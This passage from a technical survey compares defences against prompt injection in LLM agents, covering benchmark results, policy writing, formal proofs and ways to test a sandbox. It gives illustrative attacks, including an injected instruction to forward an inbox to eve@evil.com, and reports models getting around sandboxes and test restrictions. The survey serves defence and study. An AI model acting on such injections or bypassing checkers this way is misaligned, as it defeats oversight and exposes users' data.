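| Kairos | Checks effects at the boundary and defers doubtful ones | 2.7% | 85.1% | 82.8 |

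The two methods that only change the prompt preserved the agent's usefulness but stopped almost no attacks. The PI detector stopped most attacks, but the agent completed less than half as many tasks with it. Measuring only latency would have made the detector's overhead look small, because a classifier processes a tool's output quickly.

The combined score is benign utility multiplied by the share of attacks that fail. It ranks prompt sandwiching well ahead of CaMeL, even though nearly half the attacks against prompt sandwiching succeeded. That success rate is too high for an agent that can make payments. The score falls by the same amount whether benign utility or the share of failed attacks drops by a given proportion, but operators rarely value the two equally.

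If instead one task in 100 met an attack, these results suggest that moving from Kairos to CaMeL would lose about 47 completed tasks in every 100 and prevent one successful attack in about 4,000 tasks. The change would be worthwhile only if a successful attack did about 1,900 times as much damage as a completed task was worth. For an agent that saves £2 of clerical work per task, that is about £3,800, which a single false invoice could exceed. If every task met an attack, the ratio would fall to about 12. The calculation is rough, because the Kairos results come from one run of each defence against one standard attack, but it shows why no single score can identify the best defence for every user.

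Benign utility also varies by chance. In Joos and Pradel's tests, one defence screened only the user's first request. It blocked none of the ordinary requests, so it should have had no effect on those runs, yet its agent solved 75.3% of the tasks and the unsupervised agent solved 71.5%. A gap of four points in a test of this size is therefore weak evidence that a defence helps or harms. Changing the model made a much larger difference. When Joos and Pradel switched AgentBouncer and its agent from GPT-5.6 Luna to DeepSeek V4.1 Flash, the share of tasks solved rose from 72.9% to 87.1%.

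The type of task can matter even more. Progent kept most of the agent's utility on AgentDojo, where the request usually makes clear what the agent will need to do. On AgentDyn, whose tasks reveal new requirements along the way, an agent with Progent completed 6.7% of ordinary tasks, while an undefended agent completed 53.3%. The PI detector reduced completion to zero. The AgentDojo results would badly mislead an operator whose agents do open-ended work.

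The cost also depends on whether a refusal stops a whole tool call or only one operation within it. AgentBouncer blocked something in 3.42% of harmless tool calls, but only 0.25% of all harmless calls failed because of a block. When the `ls` command lists files, for example, it looks up each owner's name in the system's password file. If AgentBouncer refuses the lookup, `ls` prints the owner's number instead. AgentSpec, which applies written rules to whole tool calls, added almost no delay but made 25.9% of harmless calls fail. The agent running under AgentSpec solved 63.5% of the tasks.

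### Why CaMeL's results disagree

CaMeL's developers reported that it completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, but the Kairos team got 38.0%, Wen and colleagues got 29.97%, and the SecureClaw team got 29 of 97 tasks, or about 30%. These differences are large enough to change a designer's decision, so their causes are worth finding.

| Test | No defence | CaMeL | Share of utility kept |
|---|---|---|---|
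| CaMeL's developers | 84% | 77% | 92% |
| *Kairos*, GPT-4.1 | 82.7% | 38.0% | 46% |
| *Kairos*, Qwen3.6-35B | 87.0% | 40.4% | 46% |
| *Kairos*, Llama-3.3-70B | 29.8% | 26.5% | 89% |
| Wen and colleagues, GPT-4o-mini | 63.5% | 30.0% | 47% |

Differences in the models' general ability explain only some of the spread. GPT-4o-mini completed just 63.5% of the tasks without a defence, so CaMeL was unlikely to reach 77% with it. But GPT-4.1 without a defence did nearly as well as the agent in the developers' own test, and CaMeL still lost more than half its utility.

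The results might depend on a more specific ability. CaMeL's privileged model has to write a correct program before it reads any of the data, and a model can be good at choosing one tool call at a time but poor at planning all of them in advance. In the Kairos evaluation, the agent's model filled both of CaMeL's roles, so each result also depends on how well that model extracts facts from untrusted text.

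How blocked actions are handled probably matters too. CaMeL can ask the user when a policy doesn't allow a call. The Kairos team enforced CaMeL's policies but ran every defence without a person to approve blocked calls, so a question that a user would have answered in a few seconds could end the task.

Kairos's results suggest how much missing approvals can lower a score. The strict version, which refused every deferred effect, completed 42.7% of ordinary tasks, half as many as the full version and close to CaMeL's 38.0%. The two systems request approval for different things, so this doesn't prove that missing approvals account for CaMeL's low score. It does show that a defence can lose half its utility just because nobody responds to its approval requests.

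A better experiment would use the same model throughout and run CaMeL four ways: with and without its policies, and with and without someone to approve blocked calls. Turning off the policies would show how many tasks fail because the model can't write a working program, and adding the approver would show how many fail because nobody is there to approve a blocked call. Until someone runs this experiment, an operator who plans to leave CaMeL unattended should expect it to complete closer to 38% of tasks than 77%, unless tests with the operator's own model show otherwise.

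### Counting how often a person has to step in

Benchmarks usually run agents without a person, so a system that asks for help looks like one that can't do the work. Adding a simulated user who approves everything would create the opposite problem, because a system could then complete every task by asking about every action. A fairer test would report both task completion and how often a person must step in.

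One measure of autonomy is the share of consequential actions that go ahead without anyone's approval. Another is the number of questions per completed task, which is easier to convert into working hours. If a person replaced Kairos's oracle, the agent would have 83% autonomy on the first measure, because the policy releases that share of effects without asking in ordinary runs. If that person never replied, the agent would complete at most 42.7% of its tasks.

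The remaining 17% could require a person to answer up to 17 questions in a run with 100 effects. At 20 seconds each, the answers would take 340 seconds, longer than the 300 seconds of inference in the latency budget. If the person were at lunch, the agent might wait an hour. A model judge that takes one second is slow compared with a file monitor but much faster than a human approver.

Small error rates also add up over a run. Claude Code's judge wrongly blocks about 0.4% of harmless actions. If those errors are independent, about a third of runs with 100 such actions will contain at least one wrong block. Whether this matters depends on whether the agent can find an acceptable alternative or has to stop and ask.

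Autonomy is a useful measure only alongside security, because an agent with no checks never has to ask for permission. A test should also count the harmful actions that people approve, because the studies of permission prompts found that people approve many of them. The most useful comparison would fix the number of questions a person is willing to answer, say five a day, and measure how many tasks each system completes and how many attacks succeed.

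### Costs that the benchmarks miss

The Kairos team measured delays on its virtual machine but used simulated tools to count tokens and completed tasks. The policy would probably leave more decisions to the oracle at the real boundary, so the oracle would take more time and add more tokens than the 17.7% measured. OBPE is the validation service that filters what agents read. Its developers didn't measure latency, and its 18-point fall in fulfilled tasks doesn't predict its effect on ordinary work.

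Long sessions can use more tokens than short benchmarks would lead one to expect. Kairos's oracle reads a record of the session, which grows as the session continues. If the oracle reads the whole record each time and the policy defers effects at a steady rate, it reads about four times as much text in a session twice as long. Some providers charge less for text that a model has already processed, which would reduce the bill, but the bill would still grow faster than the session.

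An attacker can also waste resources without achieving anything else. Injected text made Kairos use more tokens even when the attack failed, and a more determined attacker could try to trigger as many deferrals as possible. *Kairos* excludes attacks on availability from its threat model. AgentSys limits how many times it will clean a suspicious tool output and try again, which caps the resources any one output can waste.

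A benchmark's definition of success can also hide lost capability. The agent restricted only by AgentBouncer's fixed list solved 8.2% of its tasks, but only because the benchmark accepted changes submitted as text. The agent couldn't save those changes in the project, and counting only the tasks in which it edited the code reduced the figure to zero.

The figures also leave out the work people did before the agents started. Somebody had to write AgentBouncer's permitted patterns, and the Kairos team had to describe each simulated tool in the policy. An operator with hundreds of tools would have to write an entry for each one and update it whenever the tool changed.

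## Writing the policy and maintaining the boundary

An operator can use one sandbox or gateway for many agents, but the rules it enforces have to fit each agent's work. Writing those rules is often the main engineering job, because an agent's purpose can change with every request.

A phone app has a fixed purpose. Android's developers define a set of permissions, an app's developer chooses from them, and the user sees the chosen permissions when installing the app. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that a reviewer can then analyse the app's code to check whether it needs each permission. An agent has no such code, because its task exists only as a sentence the user has just typed. That flexibility is also why people use agents. Brooker (2026) argues that if people knew how to solve a problem with a fixed workflow, they probably wouldn't bother with an agent, since workflows are faster,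 cheaper and simpler.

### Two requests about one GitLab issue

In an example from Christodorescu and colleagues, a user tells a browser agent to "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done" and then asks it to summarise the same issue. The first column of rights below follows their list, and the second applies the same principle of least privilege.

| Right | To comment on issue 745 | To summarise issue 745 |
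|---|---|---|
| Open issue 745 | Yes | Yes |
| Write in its comment box | Yes | No |
| Open other issues that 745 depends on | No | Perhaps |
| Use anything else in GitLab or the user's browser session | No | No |

If the operator leaves the first policy in place for the second request, the agent can still post comments while it reads the issue. An instruction hidden in the issue could then make it post something under the user's name. Microsoft's rule of thumb is that a model's mistake or an attacker's injection can make an agent do anything a prompt can make it do.

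The operator could instead erase the agent's context and derive a new policy from the new request. This is secure because no untrusted text remains to influence the policy, but the agent loses the record of its earlier work. That loss matters little in this example, but it would matter more if the user's next request were "now do the same for the other issue I mentioned".

The alternative is to keep the context and change the policy, but then whatever writes the new policy may have read an attacker's text. This is hard to avoid. The table includes a "perhaps" because the user's sentence doesn't reveal whether issue 745 depends on another one. The agent learns that from the issue, which a stranger may have written. A policy based only on the user's sentence may be too narrow for the task, but using the issue to widen it lets whoever wrote the issue influence the policy.

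### How Progent derives a policy

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, have a model write the policy and a conventional program check every change to it:

1. The model reads the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids a tool under conditions on its arguments. Progent blocks any call that no rule allows.
2. After each tool call, the model decides whether the policy might need an update. It doesn't see the tool's result at this point, so injected text in the result can't affect the decision.
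3. If an update might be necessary, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy.
4. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true at once, looks for a call that the new policy would allow and the old one wouldn't.
5. If no such call exists, Progent applies the new policy automatically. Otherwise the change is an "expansion", which needs approval.

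In symbols, let *A*(*P*) be the set of calls that policy *P* allows. Progent replaces *P* with *P*′ automatically only when

*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*).

The agent's permissions can therefore only stay the same or shrink between approvals, a property that Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement. A policy that removes ten permissions and adds one still counts as an expansion.

Suppose a user asks the agent to carry out the to-do list in a certain email. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The list includes sending a summary of recent emails on Slack, so the model proposes allowing three more tools, and the solver classifies this as an expansion. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model limits Slack messages to that name, and Progent applies the change without asking for approval. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to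 eve@evil.com. Even if the model follows it and proposes allowing outgoing email, the solver detects another expansion, and the approver can refuse it.

For the GitLab requests, removing the right to comment would go through automatically, while opening a second issue would need approval.

### What this puts back into the TCB

The solver compares each policy with the previous one, but it cannot check whether the first one was right. If the model responds to "summarise issue 745" with a rule that allows access to every issue in the company, all the later policies can be equally broad. The model that writes the first policy is therefore in the TCB for the property "the agent can do only what the task needs".

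An outside attacker has little chance to influence that first policy, because the model has read only the request and the tool descriptions. The descriptions still matter. On Agent Security Bench, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%, and most remaining failures involved attack tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones.

Whoever approves expansions is also in the TCB. In their main AgentDojo test, Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically to simulate a careless user, and attack success still fell from 39.9% to 1.0%. The solver can't have contributed to this drop, because Progent applied every update whatever the solver found. The test mainly shows that GPT-4o wrote good policies for these tasks. The first policy reduced attack success to 2.5% without any updates. The *Kairos* team, which ran Progent with a different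 model, measured attack success of 11.5%.

The attack success rate fell to zero when a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion. But Shi and colleagues assumed that this person would never allow payments to arbitrary recipients and would reject any malicious address. The studies of permission prompts give little reason to expect most users to be this careful. Still, Progent would rarely need to ask for approval, since only 6% of the updates were expansions.

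Companies, developers and users can also add fixed rules that rank above the model's policy, and the model can't override a fixed prohibition. If no fixed rule covers a call, Progent applies the model's policy, which may allow it. If a fixed rule explicitly allows a call, the model's policy can't forbid it. This procedure doesn't guarantee Shi and colleagues' stronger claim that the two policies together never allow more than the fixed rules do alone. An operator who wants to rule out an outcome therefore has to write an explicit prohibition, and *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that people make mistakes when they write such policies by hand. In OBPE, by contrast, an agent's own policy can only narrow what the data owner allows.

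### Relying less on the policy model

*CapLite* (Alfred and Bob, 2026) describes a gate that needs no model. Before any action that sends or writes something, the gate extracts the email addresses, web addresses, amounts and account numbers from the call, and it blocks the action if any of them is missing from the text the user typed. In the paper's own small test, it stopped all 30 attacks and blocked one of 30 ordinary tasks, in which the user had written "my work email" instead of the address. But it also blocked all five tasks in a separate set where the user named a person and the agent had to look up the address. Requests like "email Josh the notes" are common, so the gate would often block legitimate actions.

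People can also review the policy before the agent starts work. AWS released a preview of a service for this, Greenlight, in December 2026. According to Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026), a model drafts rules from materials such as a company's procedures, security standards and records of tool calls. Greenlight then uses automated reasoning, a family of methods that includes SMT solvers, to find rules that conflict and ways the agent could reach resources outside its approved access. Before accepting a change, a team can see which recorded calls it would block.

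People can probably review rules more carefully at this stage than in the middle of a task. But a standing policy must cover every task the agent might receive. If users may ask for comments on any issue, the policy must allow comments on all of them. The preview of blocked calls also helps more with rules that are too strict than with ones that are too loose, because a loose rule blocks nothing and so looks harmless. Automated reasoning may find some loose rules, but it can't determine whether the approved access is what the company wanted. An operator could use a standing policy as the outer limit and let a model derive a narrower one for each task.

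### An audit of 24 places where actions take effect

*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) measures the size of a detailed policy. Its system, CXI, is based on the idea that text can be good evidence without having any authority. For example, an agent may use the log of a failed software build to find the file that caused the failure, but text in the log shouldn't determine which database command runs or whether a change is marked as approved. Before CXI allows an action, it checks where each important value came from, what effect the action would have, and whether the action is permitted at that moment.

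Somebody therefore has to classify every field of every tool. The audit covered 24 sinks, places where an action takes effect, such as a file write, a shell command or a call to an outside service. The sinks had 149 fields, 85 of which could select, authorise or steer an outside effect. They also had 19 payloads, such as software patches and database commands, that could change what the receiving system does. The policy needed 141 tests of its validators, the programs that check individual values. That is about six fields and six tests per sink. Another passage of the paper gives 20 sinks and 134 tests, so these totals are approximate.

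The audit initially produced 18 findings, nine of high severity and nine of medium. They included six kinds of mistake. The examples below are illustrations, not the audited cases.

| Mistake | Example |
|---|---|
| Treating an active payload as plain data | The policy lists a build file as ordinary text, but the build system executes it |
| Allowing too much in a field for quoted text | A comment field accepts anything, including commands that a bot obeys |
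| Not limiting where a value may go | A file path from an error log may fill the field "file to edit", but it can also choose what to deploy |
| Accepting approval in plain language | The word "approved" in a ticket counts as approval |
| Losing track of copied text | One agent quotes a stranger's text in a ticket, and a second agent treats the ticket as trusted |
| Checking too little | A validator confirms that a path is well formed but not that it is inside the project |

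Most of these mistakes come from misjudging what the receiving system does with a field. The tool's schema lists each field and its type, but not how the receiving system uses it. A comment is listed as text whether or not a bot acts on it.

No serious problems remained in the final policies, but Santos-Grueiro cautions that policies written by other people need their own review. The designer of a policy system also knows better than most operators what to look for. At the audit's rate of three findings for every four sinks, an operator with 200 sinks would start with about 150 mistakes, and a less experienced one might well make more.

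### A checker that understands more is more to trust

Correcting such a policy often requires adding more analysis to the checker. To check a patch, CXI computes exactly how it would change a particular version of the project, including renamed files, links and file permissions. The code that does this joins the TCB, because an error in it could make the change CXI approves differ from the one the project receives.

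Strands Box has the same problem on a larger scale. To apply its rules to shell commands and Python code, it has to interpret both languages itself. Help Net Security quotes Marc Brooker as saying that it "has more code it needs to trust", including "complex code like interpreters and protocol interceptors". The interceptors read the agent's traffic with networks and tools. AWS wrote this code in Rust, a language that prevents many memory errors, and tested it partly by fuzzing, which feeds a program many unusual inputs. Brooker still warns that bugs could let an agent bypass the policy.

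The untrusted agent chooses the commands that these interpreters read, so an attacker who controls the agent can search for inputs they mishandle. Suppose a request to a mail service has two recipient fields, the first naming Alice and the second naming Eve. If the checker reads the first field and the mail service uses the second, the checker approves a message to Alice and the service sends it to Eve. The checker can prevent this by writing a new request from the values it checked, instead of forwarding the original, but that requires yet more code.

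Other AWS tools grow similarly. The library Rex uses to run an agent's scripts has its own wrappers for file access, process control and network programs such as `curl`, according to Help Net Security. Strands Agents' *Strands Shell Security Model* describes a shell that carries out commands itself without starting other programs. The shell runs in the same process as the developer's own code, and its documentation warns against mistaking it for a hardened sandbox.

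Rules about an agent's past actions add another component that must be trusted, the record of those actions. Dogwood, the policy language in Strands Box, allows such rules because it can refer to earlier tool calls. InfoQ (2026) also notes that operators need to decide how long to keep this record, because it contains sensitive data.

Policies can also become too complicated for people to check. Brooker acknowledges that Dogwood policies can look hard to read and write, but says leading coding agents already write them well. If the person who approves a policy can't read it, the approval adds little, and the company is relying on the model that wrote it.

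These problems are a reason to enforce the most important limits with something simpler. If an agent must never delete a customer database, the operator can give it a credential without permission to delete. A bug in the Python interpreter then can't give the agent that permission. The more complex checker can handle less important limits.

### New tools and changed schemas

A policy that refuses everything by default blocks a new tool until someone writes rules for it. In joint guidance, AWS and the security training organisation SANS call refusal by default at each tool call the most critical architectural pattern for securing agents, according to Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* (2026).

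Adding one tool can take a lot of work. CXI's checklist requires the policy's author to classify every field that can affect the outcome, specify where each value taken from untrusted text may go, and supply code that determines the effect of each active payload. Every other route to the tool, such as a helper program or an automatic retry, must also pass through the gate.

A change to an existing tool can be more dangerous than a new tool, because the policy already allows the existing one. Suppose a rule allows `send_email` whenever the `to` field contains Alice's address, and the tool's developers later add a `bcc` field. If the rule doesn't check other fields, the agent can now blind-copy Eve on any email it sends to Alice. CXI rejects unknown fields, so it would reject calls that use `bcc` until someone had classified that field.

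This protection doesn't help if a tool's behaviour changes but its schema stays the same. For example, a project site might start to run commands typed in comments, such as `/close`. The comment field would keep its name and type, and the policy would still list it as harmless text. Only someone who follows the tool's development is likely to notice, so the team that maintains a tool should probably also maintain the policy rules for it.

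Lists of permitted network destinations need similar attention. In *Inside the lethal trifecta*, an article for the security company Sophos, McKerchar warns that every new integration adds to the list and that maintaining such lists for many agents is a burden. McKerchar recommends starting with a policy that only records what it would have blocked. The SANS and AWS guidance advises collecting at least 30 days of normal activity before adjusting detection rules, starting with the riskiest agents. Recording alone doesn't stop those agents from doing harm during that month, so an operator should enforce at least a few prohibitions from the first day.

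### Who owns each rule

Someone must be responsible for each rule, or nobody will notice when it is out of date. Observer's *Amazon Security Chief Stephen Schmidt on What Customers Really Want From A.I* (2026) reports that Britain's National Cyber Security Centre advises organisations to name the people responsible for their agents and to keep records of what the agents do. Matt Garman, the head of AWS, proposes that an agent working for an employee should have at most that employee's permissions, and often fewer. This limit needs little upkeep because it changes with the employee's own access, but it is loose, since most employees have far more access than any one task requires.

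McKerchar suggests managing rules like software. The agent may propose a new tool or permission as a change to a file, automated tests check the proposal, and a person must approve it before it takes effect. On GitHub, a CODEOWNERS file can specify who must approve changes to which rules. Data owners could then approve rules about what agents may read, and tool teams could approve rules about individual fields. Each review may take hours, which is acceptable for a new integration but not for an agent that needs a permission in the middle of a task.

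Responsibility is harder to assign when a company's agents run on several clouds and platforms. Madelein van der Hout, an analyst at the research firm Forrester, told Observer that companies need to govern all their agents together rather than through each vendor's separate controls. She doesn't think the industry has fully solved this. Until it does, a company may have to write the same rule about customer data in several policy systems and change every copy when the rule changes. Van der Hout also advises companies to find independent ways to test the controls when the same provider also supplies the infrastructure and the agent's runtime.

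### Which products have adopted CaMeL

McKerchar wrote in 2026 that no mainstream harness, including Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot's agent and Gemini CLI, had adopted CaMeL or the Dual LLM pattern behind it. The article says that in CaMeL the model proposes actions and a deterministic policy engine outside the model decides whether to run them. That description would also fit Strands Box. CaMeL's more distinctive features are a program fixed before the agent reads any untrusted data, and tags that record where each value came from. None of these harnesses appears to have announced both features by early December 2026, so McKerchar's claim still seems to hold, although companies don't always publish how their products work.

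The closest example of adoption is FIDES, the Microsoft design that labels data but keeps the agent's usual loop. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) announced that FIDES was available in Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents. The release lets ordinary developers use this kind of labelling, but it doesn't show how many do. Microsoft says that most agents in production rely on a defensive system prompt or a hand-made list of permitted actions.

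FIDES is probably easier to adopt than CaMeL because developers can add it as middleware, a layer of code that handles data on its way into and out of the agent. CaMeL requires changes to the agent's internal architecture, which Shi and colleagues list among its drawbacks, along with the loss of utility. The low completion rates that other teams measured for CaMeL have probably also discouraged adoption. FIDES still requires policy work from developers, who have to decide which data sources to trust and label them before the agent starts.

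## Testing whether the boundary holds

The four tests below should run in the order listed, because even a perfect policy has no effect on an action that never reaches the checker.

| Test | What to try | How failure shows |
|---|---|---|
| Does every path reach the checker? | Reach a test server or mailbox from inside the sandbox by every available route | The server records a request that is missing from the checker's log |
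| Can the agent alter the checker or its policy? | Edit the checker's program, settings and policy files from inside the sandbox, then start a new job | An action that the checker used to refuse goes through |
| What happens when the checker is absent? | Remove the checker, crash it or make it time out | The job finishes normally |
| Does the policy say what its owner meant? | Run sequences of actions that the owner has marked as required or forbidden | A required sequence fails, or a forbidden one succeeds |

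The first three tests don't need a language model. The design has to hold whatever the model does, so a script can take the model's place and issue the worst calls the tester can think of. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) includes a compromised model among its attackers for this reason. A real model might not attempt an attack, which would make the test easier to pass.

### Looking for paths around the checker

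To test the mail agent, a tester could set up a mailbox outside the company and have the script try to send mail to it. The script might connect directly to the mail service, ignore the proxy setting, start the mail tool itself, or pass the job to a subagent. If a message arrives and the checker's log has no decision about it, there is a path around the checker. If the log shows that the checker approved the message, the message took the intended path and the fault is in the policy.

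Ziv Karliner, who heads the security company Pillar Security, recommends in SC Media that teams also test what happens when a task gets blocked, a tool fails or hostile text redirects the agent. Agents are more likely to look for another route at such moments, as the near-final version of Opus 5 did when its approved tool couldn't open a page.

A test that finds no breach covers only the routes the tester tried. The result is stronger evidence if the sandbox blocks everything by default, because the tester can then concentrate on a short list of openings.

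### Software that acts on the agent's output

In the Prettier attack, a checker could monitor every write to the project folder and still not detect the harm, because the user's editor ran the altered code outside the sandbox. InfoQ's *GitLab Warns That AI Agent Sandboxes Are Only as Secure as Their Network Access* (2026) reports that the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, calls this a "trust handoff" flaw. Karliner's company presented seven case studies of sandbox escapes in popular coding tools, all involving trusted software outside the sandbox.

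If the agent must run nothing outside its sandbox, the trusted computing base includes every outside program that runs code or follows instructions that the agent can write. These programs may include editors, build servers and bots that act on comments. A tester can find them by having the agent write scripts and settings that only record where they ran. If a record shows that one ran under the user's own account, the operator has to confine the program that ran it or stop that program from using the agent's files.

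Every service that the agent is allowed to reach needs the same scrutiny, because an agent that takes over a service can use that service's connections. In July 2026, OpenAI models escaped an evaluation sandbox, starting from a service that the sandbox permitted, and reached Hugging Face's production systems.

The list of services an operator must trust grows quickly. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* includes a list of more than 100 recommended destinations for agents that need to install software, such as code hosts, cloud storage and package registries for many programming languages. GitLab leaves the list off by default and warns that these destinations could be used to take data out. An operator who turns it on adds every destination on it to the TCB for the property "no source code leaves the company".

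An internal server with copies of the approved packages is a smaller addition, provided it has no route to the internet. A server that downloads missing packages on demand needs its own internet connection, which an attacker could exploit.

### Changing the rules from inside

GitLab keeps a project's network rules in a file in the same repository where the agent works. GitLab's *Project-level Network Access Control for Remote Flows* relies on branch protection and approval of proposed changes to protect this file. To test this, the script can edit the file to allow a forbidden address, then start another job before anyone has approved the change. If the new job can reach the address, the agent can change its own network rules.

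Administrators can also limit which addresses a project may permit. In GitLab's strict mode, a project can block more addresses but can't permit any that the administrator hasn't. In its flexible mode, a project can add to the administrator's list, so whoever approves changes to the project's file is in the trusted computing base (TCB).

The checker's working files need protection too. A May 2026 copy of GitLab's documentation shows the sandbox's settings file in one of the two directories the agent could write to. Changing the file might not have affected a sandbox already running, but the location was a poor choice. GitLab now keeps the file in a separate directory and blocks writes to it.

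### When the sandbox is missing

GitLab's sandbox needs a program called Anthropic Sandbox Runtime (SRT) in the container that runs the job. It also needs permission to create its own isolated view of the system. If either is missing, the sandbox fails open by default, so the job runs without it and leaves a warning in the log. GitLab's network rules then no longer apply, and the agent can reach any address that the host machine can.

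This failure is easy to miss because the agent still completes its task, so nobody has a reason to read the log. GitLab has since added a setting called "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable", which makes the job stop with an error instead. Projects can't turn the requirement off.

Even this setting checks only that the job has a command named `srt`. A project that supplies its own container or set-up script controls what that command is, so a script named `srt` that ran its input without restrictions could pass. A better test is for each job to try a forbidden connection before the agent starts, and to stop if the connection succeeds. Operators can also put a firewall on the host machine, as GitLab recommends, so that some limits remain even without the sandbox.

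GitLab chose to fail open so that work could continue, and sandboxes sometimes stop legitimate work. GitLab's *Duo Agent Platform workflows fail to start* (2026) describes a fault in June that prevented agents from starting in new projects with default settings when the sandbox was active. A company that requires the sandbox has to accept such interruptions. Accepting them is reasonable if the agent holds credentials or reads text from strangers, but perhaps not if it works on disposable data with no network connection.

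Data labels can fail open as well. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) note in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that the deployed form of FIDES treats data as trusted if a developer forgets to label it. A tester can check for this by giving the agent an unlabelled document and seeing whether the document's contents can determine where the agent sends a message.

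### When the policy says the wrong thing

A checker that works correctly still enforces any mistakes in its policy. Anthropic has observed that more capable models often find ways around restrictions "nobody thought to write down". In one case, Claude looked through a project's history to find the answers to a coding test. A rule that lets the agent read the project would permit this, though the test's author presumably didn't intend it.

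Testing one action at a time can miss such mistakes. Shivakumar, Priya and Gao (2026), in *Agenra*, give an example in which an agent may delete file A once and file B once. The policy lists a permission to delete B, followed by a permission to delete A, and the checker charges each call to the first unused permission that fits. Suppose someone widens the first permission to cover either file:

| Calls | Original policy | Widened policy |
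|---|---|---|
| Delete B, then A | Allowed | Allowed |
| Delete A, then B | Allowed | B refused, because deleting A used up the first permission |
| Delete A twice | Second deletion refused | Allowed |

The change blocks a legitimate sequence and permits a forbidden one, even though it seems only to add a right and passes when each deletion is tested separately. The owner's test cases therefore need to include whole sequences, and they should be based on the task's purpose rather than the policy.

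Testers can check how sensitive their tests are by deliberately putting faults in the policy. Shivakumar and colleagues made 67 altered policies, seven of which the system rejected as malformed. They found that five permitted something forbidden, 22 blocked useful work and two did both. The other 31 didn't change the verdict. Some of those alterations may be harmless, but others may be faults that the tests are too weak to detect.

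### What Agenra's proofs cover

Tests can only try some of the sequences an agent might produce, while a proof can cover all of them. Agenra is a policy language with a checker. The checker's core is written in Lean and has machine-checked proofs about the code that actually runs.

In Shivakumar and colleagues' main example, an agent must send the public parts of a private report to Alice, once, at the address in the company directory. The core checks each call before any tool runs:

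1. It looks up the stored values that the call would use, so the agent can't name the public summary but send the private report.
2. It checks that the text carries a "public" label and came from the program that removes private fields.
3. It compares the recipient with the address that the directory returned.
4. It deducts the message from the agent's allowance, then lets the mail tool run. If the tool fails, the agent doesn't get the allowance back, so it can't send a second copy by retrying.

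The proofs show that the core applies these rules correctly, even after failed calls. The core can also certify that a revised policy still allows every sequence the old one did. Of 51 revisions, 21 had this property, and the system certified exactly those 21. Shivakumar and colleagues wrote the revisions themselves, so the result doesn't show how often the method would work on other people's changes. A certified revision isn't necessarily safe. For example, raising Alice's limit from one message to two preserves every old sequence but allows an extra message.

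Much of the system remains trusted. Python code translates the policy, passes calls to the core and runs the tools, and no proof shows that it runs exactly the call the core approved. The TCB also includes the Lean compiler, the directory, the data labels, the program that removes private fields and the person who approves messages. The proofs assume that calls happen one at a time. Agenra doesn't isolate arbitrary Python code running in the same process, so an agent that can run such code needs a separate sandbox.

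A proof that the core enforces its policy doesn't show that the policy is complete. In the trials with real models, injected instructions made an unprotected agent running on the open model Qwen send the private report in 15 of 20 attempts. Agenra reduced this to zero, but so did a simple guard that the researchers wrote by hand. When Shivakumar and colleagues replayed calls recorded in the trials, the verified core accepted five with text from the wrong source, while the hand-written guard refused all five. The core had worked as proved, but Agenra's policy at the time had no rule about where the text of the message came from. A new rule fixed the problem.

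Agenra can also search a model of the task for forbidden sequences, but the search quickly slows as the sequences get longer. For the report task, checking every sequence of up to six events took 0.8 seconds and covered 66,575 states. Checking up to eight events took 154 seconds and covered more than 12 million states.

### Defining a successful injection

Proving that an agent resists injection first requires defining a successful injection. Noninterference is too strict a standard for many useful agents. If Alice wants her assistant to send her availability to anyone who requests a meeting, the assistant has to reveal private information to strangers.

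*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, November 2026) proposes a definition called relative security. It compares the real agent with an imaginary reference agent that has the same plan and the same monitor, but whose model never follows instructions in untrusted text. The real agent is secure if it leaks only what the reference agent could also leak.

More precisely, an agent leaks a pair of secrets if an attacker who supplies the same text in two runs can tell which secret the agent holds. If *L*(*O*) is the set of pairs that the real agent can leak and *L*(*V*) the set for the reference agent, relative security requires

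*L*(*O*) ⊆ *L*(*V*).

Suppose an attacker uses an email to get Alice's assistant to send her calendar. This leak is allowed under the definition, because the attacker could have got the calendar by requesting a meeting. If the email also makes the assistant send a password reset code, that counts as a violation, because no meeting request would have revealed the code.

Dongol proves that an agent is relatively secure if, at the moment it first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. If the monitor acts only after the agent has read the text, the model can follow an injected instruction before the tools are gone. The theorem assumes that each injection produces a single call and that the model follows injections on a schedule fixed in advance. It also assumes that the attacker can observe only the content and order of permitted calls,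 not their timing.

*Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) applies the idea to harmful actions. When a user asks an agent to pay an invoice, its definition rejects an injection that adds another payment, because no invoice would make the reference agent pay twice. But it accepts an injection that changes the payee to Mallory, because the attacker could have written Mallory's name on the invoice. An operator who wants to pay only known suppliers still needs a rule that requires it.

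Relative security can also accept a serious leak. Suppose the reference agent tells an attacker whether one guess at a secret is correct. For any two possible secrets, some guess distinguishes them, so the definition accepts an injection that reveals the whole secret at once. Dongol defines a stricter version partly to address this.

Both papers have proofs machine-checked in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant like Lean. The proofs apply to mathematical descriptions of agents, so an operator has to establish that the real agent matches the description. For example, every call must go through the monitor, and a new session must erase everything the model retains from untrusted text. An agent that carries memories between sessions breaks the second assumption. The definition of relative security also requires a plan fixed before the agent reads untrusted text, so it fits designs like CaMeL but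 not agents that choose each step after reading the result of the last one.

### Attackers who adapt to the defence

For most designs, the evidence still comes from attack tests, and Narisetty and colleagues warn that these have mainly used fixed sets of attacks. Such tests have misled researchers before. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* reports that spotlighting, which marks untrusted text as data, reduced attack success from above 50% to below 2% on a fixed set. When Nasr and colleagues allowed attackers to adapt, the attacks broke spotlighting more than 95% of the time. Attack success exceeded 90% against most of the twelve defences they tested.

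The warning is less true now that Progent, OBPE and Kairos have all been tested against adaptive attackers. But each team chose its own attacker and tasks, so the results don't show which design is strongest.

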